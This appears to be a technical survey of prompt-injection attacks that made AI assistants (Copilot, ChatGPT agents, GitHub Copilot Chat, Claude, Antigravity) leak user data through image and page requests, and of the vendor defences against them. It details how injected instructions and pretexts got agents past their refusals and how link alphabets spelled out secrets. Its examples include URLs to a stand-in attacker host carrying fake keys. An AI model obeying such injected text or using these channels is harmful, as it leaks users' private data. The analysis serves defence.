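GCVE's *CVE-2025-32711* (2025) shows that Microsoft and the US database both rated EchoLeak as requiring no action from the victim. Microsoft scored it higher because it judged that the harm extended beyond the vulnerable component and that an attacker could alter some data. The US database gave the two flaws identical assessments, so its scores don't reflect the main practical difference between them. EchoLeak needed only an email in the mailbox and a routine question, while the other attack had to persuade somebody to click.

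Nobody has reported a real attack using either flaw. According to Ravia, Microsoft confirmed that EchoLeak had affected no customers. The US cybersecurity agency CISA entered "none" under exploitation for EchoLeak in June 2025. Microsoft answered "No" to whether anyone had exploited SearchLeak. Most of this evidence comes from Microsoft, which ran Copilot, Teams and Bing and was better placed than its customers to find traces of an attack, but it has not explained how it looked for them.

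Microsoft had fully fixed SearchLeak on its servers by 4 June 2026, when it published the record, and customers did not need to do anything. Microsoft did not specify in the record which of the three weaknesses it repaired. The attack needed all three, so repairing one would have stopped it but might have left the others usable in a different attack.

Varonis also found two flaws in Copilot Personal, the version for individuals, that an attacker could exploit with one click from the user. In *Reprompt*, a link made Copilot send personal data to the attacker by fetching web addresses, because the check against leaks covered only the first request. Microsoft has patched this flaw. In *CoSnitch* (2026), a link made Copilot read data from connected services such as Gmail and send it out through its tool for fetching pages. Microsoft patched CoSnitch on 18 August 2026, and Varonis has not seen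 anyone exploit it.

### Permitted domains that fetch other addresses

EchoLeak and SearchLeak both got past the CSP through a server that Microsoft owned and had good reason to trust. The attacker did not control Teams or Bing, but each service fetched an address it received, as it was designed to do. Varonis concludes that any permitted domain that fetches user-supplied addresses is a possible route for stolen data, and advises security teams to review their lists for such domains.

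Large websites often run services of this kind to make link previews, search by image, resize pictures or embed content from elsewhere. A broad entry such as `*.example.com` makes them easy to miss, since it covers every service the company runs under that name, including ones another team adds years later. According to Chrome for Developers' *Connection Allowlists origin trial*, the complexity of CSP often leads developers to write policies that are too broad.

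A developer can do better by keeping the images for an assistant's answers on a host that only stores files, and by permitting just the folder they are in:

```
Content-Security-Policy: img-src https://images.example.com/answers/
```

The host must not fetch anything on request, because the narrower rule would not help if the fetching service were in the permitted folder. Organisations may also find the rule hard to adopt if their answers legitimately include images from many internal sites. Some applications can avoid the problem by displaying only images that their own code has selected, and none that the model writes.

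The team responsible for a fetching service can also limit its use. SharePoint's feature was of little use to Aim Labs because the victim had to accept an invitation first. The Teams service had no such requirement, so it made a difficult attack practical. A service could also fetch only from domains its owner has approved, but this would defeat the purpose of an image search meant to work with pictures from anywhere.

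A new, stricter browser control doesn't close this gap. West's proposal replaces CSP's separate lists with a single list of the places a page may connect to, whatever the type of request, so it would block a font request or an early connection that a developer had forgotten to restrict. Report URI, a service that collects reports of blocked connections for website owners, says the control shipped in Chrome 152 in August 2026. But it applies only to connections the page makes, so a page allowed to contact Bing could still send Bing an address at attacker.example.

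## ChatGPT: checking each exact address before it is loaded

ChatGPT had the same weakness with images two years before EchoLeak. In early 2023 it displayed any image whose address the model wrote, and OpenAI at first declined to change this. The company began checking image addresses in December 2023, but researchers kept finding addresses that passed the check and could still be used to extract data. In January 2026 OpenAI published a stricter rule, under which ChatGPT loads an address automatically only if that exact address is already public.

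### An image leak that OpenAI called a feature

Roman Samoilenko discovered the leak at the end of March 2023. Willison (2023) described the attack in *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version*. A website added an instruction for ChatGPT to the text that visitors copied from it. When a visitor pasted the text into a chat, the model put data from the conversation into the address of an image. The image was a single pixel, so the visitor was unlikely to notice it.

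Rehberger found the same weakness a few days later and reported it to OpenAI on 9 April. Samoilenko's victim had to paste the attacker's text, but Rehberger pointed out that plugins would remove that step. Plugins were add-ons that connected ChatGPT to outside services, and some read web pages or video transcripts for the user. In his 2023 post *ChatGPT Plugins*, Rehberger showed how a malicious website could make the model summarise the conversation and add the summary to an image address. The stolen text included "TooManySecrets123" from earlier in the chat.

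OpenAI replied that displaying images this way was a feature and that it planned no change. Rehberger had also reported the same problem in Bing Chat to Microsoft. Microsoft generally blocked such images with a CSP in May 2023, according to Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Explains URL-Based Data Exfiltration Mitigations in New Paper*.

### The first check and its gaps

In December 2023, the day after Rehberger stole a volunteer's conversation in a live demonstration, OpenAI introduced its first fix, a service called url_safe. When an answer contained an image, the ChatGPT web page sent the image's URL to this service and displayed the image only if the reply was "safe". Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability* shows the service rejecting a URL on Rehberger's server that had an email address in its query.

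OpenAI did not publish url_safe's criteria for accepting an address. Anyone can read a website's CSP, but url_safe ran on OpenAI's servers, so outsiders had to infer the criteria by submitting addresses and studying the replies. Some replies looked arbitrary. When Rehberger submitted two image addresses that differed by a single letter, url_safe accepted one and rejected the other.

ChatGPT's iPhone app did not use the check, so the original attack still worked there. Rehberger suggested moving the check to OpenAI's servers, where it would cover every app. Willison (2023), in *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT Data Leak Vulnerability*, called the fix "half-baked" and found it odd that OpenAI hadn't simply blocked images from outside domains.

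The security company Imperva later worked out part of the service's logic in *From ChatBot To SpyBot*. The service mainly checked whether the submitted address appeared in the text of the conversation, and accepted it if it did. This is a sensible test for theft because an address already in the conversation is not one the model has just built around a secret. But the service trusted some domains more broadly. On openai.com, for example, it accepted any path and any query. Imperva warned that an attacker who found a redirect on such a domain might get around the check.

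### AgentFlayer: API keys from a connected Google Drive

By 2025, a feature called Connectors let ChatGPT search a user's files in services such as Google Drive, SharePoint and GitHub. Zenity Labs' *AgentFlayer* describes how an attacker could use a document to exploit this feature against the user. OODA Loop's *A Single Poisoned Document Could Leak Secret Data via ChatGPT* reports that Michael Bargury and Tamir Ishay Sharbat presented the attack at the Black Hat security conference in August 2025, using API keys in a demonstration Drive account.

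The attacker hid the instruction in tiny white text in an ordinary-looking document. The victim uploaded the document to ChatGPT and asked for a summary. The hidden text said that the user did not really want a summary, then told a story about a developer who was about to miss a deadline and needed some API keys from Drive. It instructed the model to search for the keys, put them in the address of an image and leave the search out of its answer. Zenity added the story because ChatGPT tends to avoid handling sensitive data.

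The model followed the instructions, but the first attempt failed. The image address pointed to a public service that developers use to test web requests, and url_safe rejected the address, so the browser never requested the image.

Zenity then found that url_safe accepted addresses on a large cloud storage service, where any customer can store a picture and read the log of requests for it. With a fake key and a reserved domain, the new address would look like this:

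```
https://storage.example/attacker-account/picture.png?FAKE-KEY-123
```

This time the image appeared in the answer, and the request to load it left the keys in the attacker's log. EchoLeak and SearchLeak needed a trusted server that would forward a request to the attacker. AgentFlayer needed no forwarding, because the attacker was a customer of the service on the trusted domain and could read the keys in the log there.

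In Zenity's own account of the attack on ChatGPT Connectors, the victim has to upload the poisoned file to ChatGPT and then doesn't have to click anything. But OECD's *ChatGPT Connectors Vulnerability Enables Zero-Click Data Theft via Poisoned Documents* (2025) describes the attack as "requiring no user interaction", and The Decoder's *An invisible prompt in a Google Doc made ChatGPT access data* reports that sharing a document with someone was enough. People often upload files from others, and Zenity noted that a malicious employee could add hidden text to many documents that colleagues were likely to upload. Zenity did not report how often the attack succeeded.

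OpenAI had known about the storage domain since October 2024, when Rehberger reported it along with other ways around url_safe. Embrace The Red's *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection* used the domain to steal material from a user's recent conversations, which ChatGPT's chat history feature placed in the context of each new one. A malicious PDF could make the model send that material out even if the user had no connected services. Rehberger advised OpenAI to tighten the check, publish the list of trusted domains and let business customers manage it.

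According to Embrace The Red, OpenAI strengthened url_safe around August 2025 and stopped the attacks Rehberger had demonstrated. These included the route through the storage domain, which AgentFlayer also depended on.

### ShadowLeak: the request came from OpenAI's servers

Radware's *ShadowLeak* describes an attack that avoided url_safe. It targeted Deep Research, a ChatGPT agent that spends 5 to 30 minutes reading sources and then writes a report. Users can connect it to their Gmail accounts and let it browse the web at the same time, which meets all three conditions of the lethal trifecta.

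In the demonstration, the victim's inbox contained a genuine message from human resources with an employee's name and home address. The attacker sent another message, supposedly about a company restructuring, with instructions for the agent to find the employee's details and look them up at the attacker's URL. These instructions could be hidden in the message's formatting. The victim later asked Deep Research to search the day's emails for information about a new employee process. The agent read both messages and opened the attacker's URL with the name and home address in it, and nothing about this appeared on the victim's screen.

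Radware, a security company, needed several attempts to write an email that made the agent send personal data to an outside address. The agent refused a plain request to do this, and it also refused when the email claimed that the user had asked for it. In later attempts, it treated the address as suspicious and searched for it on the web instead of opening it.

The researchers then asked the agent what tools it had and learned the name of the one that opened web pages. It also displayed part of its reasoning, which helped them see where each attempt failed. When the email named the tool, the agent sometimes tried to use it, but the request often failed. Telling it to keep trying helped, though it sometimes opened the address without the data. Radware solved this problem by having the agent disguise the data first, supposedly as a security measure.

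Radware reports a 100% success rate for the final version "in repeated tests". OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) prints part of the same email and says it worked 50% of the time in testing. Neither company gives the number of runs. The two figures may describe different versions of the email, because Radware used several and sent OpenAI a more reliable one the day after its first report. Either rate would be high enough for an attacker, who can send the email to many people.

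Deep Research made the request from OpenAI's servers, so a CSP could not have blocked it and the victim's employer could not have seen it in the company's network traffic. Radware also found no equivalent of url_safe for the addresses the agent opened. The agent could send data to any server, even though OpenAI had since 2023 been checking the images ChatGPT displayed.

Radware reported the flaw on 18 June 2025. OpenAI fixed it in early August without telling Radware, and marked it as resolved on 3 September. Radware's *ShadowLeak* (2025), published on 18 September, states that the same method could have exposed credentials and business documents. The demonstration extracted only a name and address, but the agent could read the rest of the mailbox.

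Radware's *ZombieAgent* reports that after these attacks, ChatGPT would open an address only exactly as it had received it, with nothing added. Radware got around this restriction too, by having the agent choose among addresses prepared in advance. OpenAI fixed that flaw on 16 December 2025.

### Why OpenAI did not rely on trusted domains

When OpenAI published its rule in January 2026, it gave two reasons why letting the agent open links only to well-known websites would not be enough.

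An attacker can use redirects to get past a safety check that looks only at the first domain. A website can answer a request by sending the visitor to a different address, and many legitimate sites do this, for instance to count clicks on outgoing links. A link that starts on a trusted site can therefore end at the attacker's server.

*OpenAI ChatGPT url_safe Mechanism Bypass* (2025), by the security company Tenable, reports that url_safe always accepted addresses on bing.com. Bing's search results use bing.com links that redirect to the listed pages, which Tenable called "an open redirect as a service". Any site in Bing's search index therefore had a bing.com address that led to it, so an attacker only had to get a page into the index.

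The attacker could not change these links, so no single link could carry an unknown secret, and Tenable had to spell the data out with a set of them. Tenable's *HackedGPT* (2025) describes a full attack that used these links. ChatGPT left web browsing to a separate model, SearchGPT, which had no access to the user's conversation or saved memories and so had no user data to leak. Instructions on a web page could still reach ChatGPT, because SearchGPT's answer became part of the conversation. Tenable put an instruction for SearchGPT in a blog comment, and SearchGPT's summary of the blog then included a further instruction for ChatGPT. When the user sent another message, ChatGPT read the summary and followed that instruction, loading images through the Bing links.

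Tenable reported the Bing weakness in December 2024, and its advisory lists the weakness as unresolved. OpenAI told Tenable in July 2025 that it had improved the check, according to Tenable's *OpenAI ChatGPT Prompt Injection via ?q= Parameter in Web Interface* (2025). But in November 2025, Tenable published a successful demonstration of the full attack on ChatGPT with GPT-5, which was released that August.

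OpenAI's other reason for not relying on a list of popular sites was that it would produce too many warnings. People visit far more sites than such a list could cover, so a strict one would often warn them about harmless pages. They would get used to clicking through the warnings and might also click through a justified one.

AgentFlayer had exposed a further problem, which OpenAI's announcement does not mention. Many domains host material from thousands of unrelated customers, so an attacker can control an account on a reputable company's servers.

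### The exact-address rule

OpenAI calls the mechanism Safe Url. It depends on a crawler, a program that finds web pages by following links. The crawler records the public addresses it finds and has no access to users' conversations or accounts. When an agent is about to load an address by itself, ChatGPT checks whether the crawler has recorded that exact address. If it has, the agent can load the address; otherwise, ChatGPT treats it as unverified.

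Suppose a user asks about battery recycling, and the agent wants to read this article:

```
https://news.example/battery-recycling
```

The crawler found the article last month through a link on the newspaper's front page. The address matches the one the crawler recorded, so the agent opens it without asking the user.

Now suppose that an injected instruction tells the model to add the user's API key to the same address:

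```
https://news.example/battery-recycling?ref=FAKE-KEY-123
```

The newspaper's server would probably return the same article, since websites often ignore query parameters they don't recognise. But the crawler has never encountered this address, because nobody has published a link with the user's key in it, so the agent can't open it automatically, even though the domain is reputable and the article is public.

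A domain list would treat some addresses quite differently:

| Address | List that trusts only news.example | Exact-address rule |
|---|---|---|
| `https://news.example/battery-recycling` | Loads | Loads |
| `https://news.example/battery-recycling?ref=FAKE-KEY-123` | Loads, with the key | Does not load automatically |
| `https://small-blog.example/first-post`, which the crawler has seen | Blocks or warns | Loads |
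| `https://attacker.example/collect?data=FAKE-KEY-123` | Blocks or warns | Does not load automatically |

The rule works because the attacker doesn't know the secret in advance. To get the address with the key into the crawler's records, the attacker would have to publish that address first, which requires already having the key. The crawler must also be independent of conversations, as OpenAI says it is. If it collected addresses from chats, one that contained a user's key could enter the records because a model had written it.

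This rule makes redirects much less useful to an attacker. The model controls only the address it requests, so a redirect can deliver a secret only if that first address contains it, and an address containing the secret fails to match. The attacker's remaining option is to have the model choose among several public addresses, so that its choice reveals information.

Some harmless addresses also fail the check. A page published an hour ago may not be in the records yet, and a private link to a shared document should never be in them. As Rehberger understands it, ChatGPT makes an exception for an address the user types into the chat and treats it as safe for the rest of that session. The exception is reasonable because the user chose the address before the model could add anything to it.

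### What happens when an address fails

ChatGPT may tell the agent to find another source, in which case the user might not notice anything. Otherwise it shows a warning, headed "Check this link is safe", that the link is unverified and may share data from the conversation with another site. The warning includes the full address, which the user can copy or open.

The warning makes the leak visible, but the user can still allow it. Someone who sees their own API key at the end of an address may well stop. In ShadowLeak, the agent had encoded the name and home address as a string of letters and numbers, which few people would recognise as their data. The warning is most useful if it appears rarely enough for people to read it, and OpenAI makes the same argument against strict domain lists.

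OpenAI says the mechanism also covers pages and bookmarks that the agent opens in Atlas, OpenAI's web browser, as well as Deep Research's searches and page visits. Searches are checked because a query can carry private data, just as a web address can. ChatGPT Apps and Canvas, where ChatGPT can build small applications, use a similar approach. The applications run in a sandbox, an isolated environment that detects unexpected attempts to contact other servers and asks the user for consent.

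OpenAI describes these measures as a way to limit the harm after an attack has fooled the model. It compares an agent to a customer service worker who can give refunds. Some customers will lie, and staff can't spot every lie, so the company limits how much they can refund. OpenAI thinks programs that scan incoming text for injected instructions have the same difficulty, and says they usually miss well-developed attacks. ChatGPT's training led it to refuse in most attempts OpenAI knows of, and Safe Url is for the remaining cases. Radware's experience fits this account, since the agent refused the early emails and gave in to a later one.

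### The promise and the products it covers

OpenAI promises only to prevent an agent from "quietly leaking user-specific data through the URL itself" when it loads a page or image. It does not promise that a page is trustworthy or free of injected instructions, or that a site won't try to trick the user. An instruction on a public page can still make ChatGPT give a wrong answer.

OpenAI described the technical details in a paper, *Preventing URL-Based Data Exfiltration in Language-Model Agents*. Rehberger, who had first reported the problem almost three years earlier, welcomed the paper and called the new defence "a significant improvement", although not a complete solution. Attacks had become more complicated, but small amounts of data could still leak through the choice of which known address to load. The paper notes this limitation.

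Rehberger's last concern was that a developer at OpenAI might build a new feature without knowing that the check exists, leaving it unprotected. This had happened before. The iPhone and Mac apps lacked the first version of url_safe, and Deep Research could open any address until the summer of 2025.

A check on the pages and images that ChatGPT loads does not cover data that leaves by another path. Check Point Research's *ChatGPT Data Leakage via a Hidden Outbound Channel* (2026) describes one such path. ChatGPT can run code in an isolated environment that is not supposed to contact the internet, but a single malicious prompt could send a user's messages and uploaded files out of it. OpenAI fixed the flaw on 20 February 2026, and The Hacker News (2026) reported no evidence that anyone had exploited it.

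That same month OpenAI introduced a stricter option called Lockdown Mode, at first only for organisations. According to OpenAI's *Introducing Lockdown Mode and Elevated Risk labels in ChatGPT* (2026), personal accounts got it in June. In this mode, ChatGPT reads only stored copies of web pages, so browsing sends no live requests outside OpenAI's network. Images in answers, Deep Research and several other features are limited or unavailable. OpenAI recommends the mode for people at higher risk, such as executives and security teams, and says most users don't need it.

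Willison (2026), in *OpenAI Help*, praised Lockdown Mode because its limits are deterministic, but also inferred from its existence that ChatGPT's default settings do not robustly protect against a determined attacker. That inference seems fair, because by default a user can approve an unverified address, and an agent can make live requests to any address the crawler has seen.

Lockdown Mode also had a flaw, as The Hacker News' *Researchers Bypass ChatGPT Lockdown Mode to Exfiltrate Chats Without User Interaction* (2026) reports. ChatGPT can preview web pages it writes, and the preview normally cannot contact other servers without the user's consent. Check Point found that a pop-up window opened from the preview could escape these restrictions. An attacker could use a crafted prompt or a shared chat to steal messages this way, and in the desktop app the victim did not have to click anything.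 OpenAI fixed the flaw on 18 September 2026.

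## Leaking a secret by choosing among permitted links

Under OpenAI's rule, ChatGPT opens an address automatically only if a crawler has already recorded that exact address, so an injected instruction can't make it open a new one that contains a key. But the model still chooses which recorded addresses to open. For example, an attacker could own two public pages that the crawler has recorded, one about tea and one about coffee. An injected instruction tells the model to open the tea page if the user's company is planning layoffs, and the coffee page otherwise. Neither address contains private data, but the attacker can learn the answer by checking the server's log to see which page was opened.

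With more pages, an attacker can spell out text. Researchers used this method against GitHub Copilot Chat and ChatGPT in 2025 and against Claude in 2026, although each had a rule against newly written addresses.

### How much one choice can carry

A bit is the amount of information in the answer to a yes-or-no question when both answers are equally likely. A request for one of N pages carries up to log2(N) bits, the number of times 1 must be doubled to reach N. Choosing between two pages carries up to one bit, and choosing among four carries up to two. With 36 pages, one for each letter and digit, each request carries up to about 5.2 bits, and with a thousand pages, up to about 10.

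A random six-digit code has a million possible values, or 19.9 bits. With 36 pages, leaking it takes four requests, which can distinguish about 1.7 million codes, since three can distinguish only 36 × 36 × 36 = 46,656. With a thousand pages, two requests are enough because they can distinguish exactly a million. For any random secret, the number of requests needed is its size in bits divided by the bits per request, rounded up. The last column is for a 240-bit key, such as forty random characters from an alphabet of 64.

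| Pages the agent may open | Bits per request | Requests for a six-digit code | Requests for a 240-bit key |
|---|---|---|---|
| 2 | 1 | 20 | 240 |
| 27 | 4.8 | 5 | 51 |
| 36 | 5.2 | 4 | 47 |
| 64 | 6 | 4 | 40 |
| 1,000 | 10.0 | 2 | 25 |

A real attack may need more requests than these minimums. To send a six-digit code in four requests, the model would have to convert it to base 36, and it might make a mistake. Opening one page per digit is simpler but takes six requests. With a thousand pages, the attacker can reach the minimum without this conversion by assigning a page to each number from 000 to 999 and having the model send half the code at a time.

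Mistakes matter more for long secrets. If the model opens the right page 99% of the time, it gets 47 choices in a row right about 62% of the time. At 95% accuracy, that falls to 9%, although it would still get four in a row right 81% of the time. A key doesn't work if even one character is wrong, whereas a misspelled name is usually still readable. Lan and colleagues found that splitting a secret across several requests made the theft less reliable.

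### What caching, reordering and limits change

The figures in the table assume that every request reaches the attacker's server in the right order. A program that caches pages reuses its saved copy of each one, so a second request for the same page may never reach the server. Requests sent close together can also arrive out of order. Rehberger noted both obstacles in 2023. In 2026 he suggested on Embrace The Red that OpenAI keep repeat requests from reaching the server, by having ChatGPT cache each page for a few minutes or refuse to open the same address twice in a session.

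The next table gives the minimum number of requests under these conditions.

| What the attacker can see | Code, 36 pages | Key, 36 pages | Code, 1,000 pages | Key, 1,000 pages |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Every request, in order | 4 | 47 | 2 | 25 |
| The first request for each page, in order | 4 | Impossible | 2 | 25 |
| Which pages the agent opened, but not the order | 6 | Impossible | 3 | 41 |

If each of 36 pages can appear only once, the log can hold at most about 140 bits, which is too little for the key. Without the order of the requests, it holds only 36 bits, one for each page that the agent did or didn't open. The six-digit code fits in either case. The attacker can recover the code even if its two halves are the same. For example, if the code is 417417 and the second request for page 417 never arrives, the attacker can infer the repetition from the single request.

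An attacker with enough pages can avoid both problems by assigning each page a character and a position, so that one page means "7 in third place". The model then never has to request the same page twice, and the order of the requests doesn't matter. This takes 60 pages and 6 requests for a six-digit code, or 2,560 pages and 40 requests for a 40-character key drawn from a 64-character alphabet.

OpenAI's rule requires the crawler to have recorded all those pages beforehand, which makes the attack harder to prepare. But Rehberger points out that anyone with a fairly large website or blog probably has 36 pages in the index already. An attacker could also publish thousands of pages and explain in the injected instruction what each one stands for.

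Limiting the number of requests caps the leak more firmly. Five requests can leak at most 26 bits if there are 36 pages to choose from, and 50 bits if there are a thousand. An attacker who had stolen 50 bits of a 240-bit key would still have to guess the other 190, which is infeasible. The same limit does not protect a six-digit code, because even three requests with 36 pages would narrow a million possible codes to about 21, and some services allow that many guesses.

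The limit also has to hold across conversations. A key stays the same until its owner replaces it, so an attacker who can reach the same assistant repeatedly could collect it in pieces, whereas a one-time code would expire before the attacker had all of it.

Anthropic's *Web fetch tool*, the developer documentation for Claude's page-fetching tool, describes the `max_uses` setting, which limits the number of fetches per request. It has no default, so fetches are unlimited unless a developer sets it. According to the documentation's Chinese edition, *網頁擷取工具*, the tool is on by default in Managed Agents, a version of Claude's agents that Anthropic runs for developers, and the setting isn't available there.

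An agent's requests can also carry information through their number, order or timing. *Actions Speak Louder than Words* (Liang, Deng and colleagues, 2026) compared these signals with the choice of page by offering agents four references and trying to infer which one matched the agent's current task. When the agents responded, the choice of page revealed the answer 93.8% of the time, compared with 73.5% for the number of requests, 67.9% for their order and 58.6% for their timing. With sixteen references, the accuracy of inferring the task from the choice of page fell to 50%. This decline probably overstates the difficulty of spelling out a key, because those agents were judging which subject was most relevant, which is more ambiguous than finding the page for the letter "k".

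### CamoLeak: an alphabet of signed images

GitHub is a website where developers discuss code and store it, along with its history, in folders called repositories. In October 2025, Legit Security's *CamoLeak* described how an outsider could use GitHub's assistant, Copilot Chat, to steal text from private repositories.

The attacker hid an instruction in the description of a pull request, which is a proposed change to a project's code, using a type of comment that GitHub allows but does not display on the page. The usual notification to the project's owner didn't show the hidden text either. When another user asked Copilot Chat to explain the pull request, the instruction entered Copilot's context. Copilot had that user's permissions, so it could read the user's private repositories.

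GitHub's Content Security Policy allowed images only from GitHub's own domains. GitHub displays pictures from other websites through a server called Camo, which fetches them for the browser. As the Teams and Bing cases showed, a permitted server that fetches outside addresses can carry secrets past such a policy. GitHub had guarded against this by adding a cryptographic signature to each Camo address. Camo fetches a picture only if the signature is valid, and the model couldn't produce a valid signature for an address it had just written.

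But anyone could get GitHub to sign addresses in advance by submitting text with outside images through its public API. Legit Security's researcher got a signed image address for each letter and symbol and listed them all in the hidden instruction. The model then wrote out the private text as a row of images. Camo fetched them from the researcher's server, which returned a transparent one-pixel image each time, so the user saw nothing unusual. The researcher also varied repeated addresses slightly to prevent caching. A rule that accepted only exact addresses would have blocked those variations.

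In the main demonstration, Copilot leaked the description of an unpatched security flaw from a problem report in a private project. The researcher also got it to search the victim's code for "AWS_KEY", a name developers might give a key for Amazon's cloud services, and send out the result. Leaking a forty-character key would take only forty tiny images, which can fit in a single answer.

Legit Security rates the flaw's severity at 9.6 out of 10. The researcher found it in June 2025, and GitHub had turned off all images in Copilot Chat to fix it by 14 August.

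### ZombieAgent: links prepared in an email

After the ShadowLeak attack, ChatGPT could open a link from an email only if it left the URL unchanged. Radware therefore sent an email with a separate link for each letter and digit, and another for a space. When the victim later asked ChatGPT to do something in Gmail, ChatGPT read the email, found the private data and opened the links one at a time to spell it out.

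Radware numbered the links to keep the characters in order. With a reserved domain, the name "Ana" would look like this:

```
https://attacker.example/a0
https://attacker.example/n1
https://attacker.example/a2
```

The two copies of "a" have different addresses, so a cache would not hide the second request. Covering ten positions takes 360 links, because each position needs one link for each of the 26 letters and ten digits.

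Radware's published example leaks a person's name after converting it to lowercase. This works well for names, but a key that mixes uppercase and lowercase letters would lose its capitalization, and the attacker would have to guess the case of each letter. An attacker who wanted keys could add links for the uppercase letters. Radware says the method could reach data in Gmail, Outlook, Google Drive and GitHub, as well as the user's chat history.

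The researchers also found a way to continue the theft across conversations. ChatGPT can save notes about a user in its memory and consult them in later conversations. If the user uploaded a malicious file, instructions in the file could make ChatGPT save a note telling it to read the attacker's email and follow the instructions there whenever the user sent a message. A limit on requests per conversation would be much less effective against this version, because the limit would reset with each new conversation.

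Radware reported the flaw on 26 September 2025 and three days later sent an improved version of the attack, which succeeded in 100% of an unstated number of runs. Bugcrowd, the company through which Radware submitted the report, reproduced the attack the next day. OpenAI fixed the flaw on 16 December. According to the news report *ChatGPT falls to new data-pilfering attack*, ChatGPT now opens a link from an email only if the address is in a public index or the user has entered it in the chat. An attacker can therefore no longer get ChatGPT to accept a new address just by including it in an email.

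### Claude: a page for every next letter

Paul (2026) tested the ordinary Claude assistant in *The Memory Heist*. Anthropic's software summarises a user's recent conversations every day and adds the summary to each new one. Claude can also search older conversations, and it reads web pages with a tool called `web_fetch`. Paul first asked Claude to open a page on a test server with the user's name in the address, but the tool blocked the request.

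The tool accepted an address if the user had typed it, if it appeared in Claude's search results, or if it was linked from a page the tool had already fetched. The last condition let Claude browse a website by following its links, but it also let the website's owner decide which addresses Claude could open next. Willison (2025) had noticed this when Anthropic released the tool for developers, and hoped for a stricter rule that accepted only addresses from the user.

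Paul built a site whose front page linked to one page for each letter of the alphabet. Each of those pages linked to every possible next letter, and the server created the pages as Claude asked for them. For a user called Ana, the log would show:

```
GET /a
GET /an
GET /ana
```

Caching and repeat limits would not have helped here, because every address was new. The order of arrival didn't matter, since the longest address contained the whole name. In CamoLeak and ZombieAgent, the attacker had to prepare all the addresses beforehand, but Paul's server could add permitted addresses during the attack.

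Claude spelled out a name when Paul asked directly, but did so less reliably when the instructions were on a web page. After several pretexts failed, Paul disguised the site as a coffee shop behind a security check with instructions for AI assistants to identify their users. *How I tricked Claude into leaking your deepest, darkest secrets* (Willison, 2026) reports that only Claude received this version of the page, so anyone checking the site in a browser would not have seen the instructions.

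The attack obtained Paul's name, employer and home city, but no credential. The blogger dyb writes in *The Read-Only Lie* that Claude had inferred the city from the name of a school programming competition, although Paul had never stated it. A home city can help someone answer a security question, but doesn't by itself give access to an account.

Each of Paul's pages offered 27 links, one for each letter and one for the hyphen. dyb estimates that the attack took about 30 fetches and could have carried up to 143 bits. At the same rate, a 240-bit key would take 51 fetches, or 40 if each page had 64 links, so the channel could have carried a key. Paul did not test whether Claude would spell one out. It might well refuse, since the pretext gave it a plausible reason to share a name but not a password.

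Anthropic told Paul that it had already found the problem internally, and paid no reward. Willison reported that by 15 July 2026 Anthropic had stopped `web_fetch` from following links in the pages it fetches. Neither Willison nor dyb says whether this change also covers the version developers use in their own programs. Developers can check by testing whether their agent still opens a link that appears only in a fetched page.

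### What remains possible, and what the fixes cost

In all three cases, the attacker could add addresses to the permitted set by getting GitHub to sign them, putting them in an email or linking to them from a web page. Each fix removed that ability or stopped the requests. The fixes differ in how much choice they leave the model and how much they inconvenience users.

GitHub's fix leaves the least room for this attack. Copilot Chat no longer loads images, so it can't spell out a secret through image requests. Users lose only the pictures in its answers, which matter little in an assistant that mostly discusses code. The fix does not cover links that a user clicks. In an earlier test, Legit Security's researcher had Copilot put encoded text from a private repository into an ordinary link, and the report doesn't mention any change to links.

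ChatGPT can still open any public page that OpenAI's crawler has recorded, so an attacker who owns 36 such pages can still get 5.2 bits per request. The attacker must first get the pages into the index, and the model must then make the right choices without stopping. These requirements are a serious obstacle to stealing a long key, but a smaller one to stealing a short code or the answer to a yes-or-no question. The protection inconveniences users when the crawler hasn't yet found a new page, or when they need a private link that should never be in a public index.

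Claude's users lost more, because an assistant that can't follow links has trouble with software manuals, long articles split over several pages and any website where the useful page is two clicks from the front page. The user can paste in the next address, or Claude can try to find the page through a search. But search results are still permitted, so an attacker with several pages in the search index may still be able to leak data through which one Claude fetches. If a search returned ten of the attacker's pages, Claude could send one digit with each fetch, and a six-digit code would take six fetches. This is an inference from the remaining rule, and Paul's attack did not use search results.

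dyb suggests a compromise, in which Claude follows links only on websites that the user has named in that conversation. This would restore most ordinary browsing and prevent a site that Claude came across by itself from leading it through a set of links. It would not help if the user had sent Claude to the malicious site.

Another option is to detect the attack as it happens. Paul's site produced a long run of fast requests to one domain, each address one character longer than the last, and dyb thinks a program could recognise that pattern with few false alarms. An attacker could easily change the pattern, though, for example by using whole words as page names. A request limit applies whatever the pages are called, but it interferes with legitimate research, where an agent may need to read dozens of pages.

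Restricting the model's choice is harder when choosing is part of its normal work. Liang and colleagues built SNOOP, a system that infers what a user is asking about from the references an agent decides to read. A link on an ordinary page leads the agent to the attacker's site, which offers references on broad subjects and then on narrower ones within the subject the agent picks. The agent only has to pick the most relevant reference, as it normally would, without looking up a secret or encoding anything.

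The researchers tested SNOOP on stored copies of web pages, using four agents, each with three language models. It needed about 6.5 rounds of choices per question. On 500 questions from StackExchange, its F1 score was 0.89, excluding the roughly 6% of attempts that produced no usable trail. F1 ranges from 0 to 1 and rewards finding the right concepts without adding wrong ones. Four existing defences changed SNOOP's scores by no more than 0.03. The experiment did not include an exact-address rule like ChatGPT's, which would make pages created during the attack much harder to use.

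This method reveals interests, health worries or business plans. It is a poor way to steal a credential, because an API key has no bearing on which articles an agent reads during ordinary research. To steal a credential this way, an attacker still needs the model to follow an injected instruction.

Liang and colleagues propose that the agent's software fetch a fixed number of pages, selected without reference to the user's private information, and let the model choose among the local copies. The attacker's server then receives the same kind of requests whichever copies the model chooses. In their tests this cut SNOOP's score from 0.89 to 0.39 without adding work for the language model, although the software has to download pages that go unread. ChatGPT's Lockdown Mode goes further by reading only stored copies. The user loses access to live pages, which matters for a train timetable or a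 share price but much less for an encyclopedia article.

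## Coding agents: keys in project files

Coding agents write and test software on a developer's computer, where the software's keys are also stored. Antigravity, a coding tool that Google released in November 2025, would open a new address containing a whole key. PromptArmor's *Google Antigravity Exfiltrates Data* describes an attack, shared by Willison (2025) on 25 November, in which a web page posing as a software guide made Antigravity do this. An attacker has to spell out a key one page at a time only if the product blocks addresses that the model has just written.

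### Why coding agents are exposed

Most programs need credentials, for instance to reach a database or take payments. Developers avoid writing these into the code, because they share the code with others. They often keep them in a text file called `.env` in the project's folder:

```
PAYMENTS_API_KEY=FAKE-KEY-123
DATABASE_PASSWORD=not-a-real-password
```

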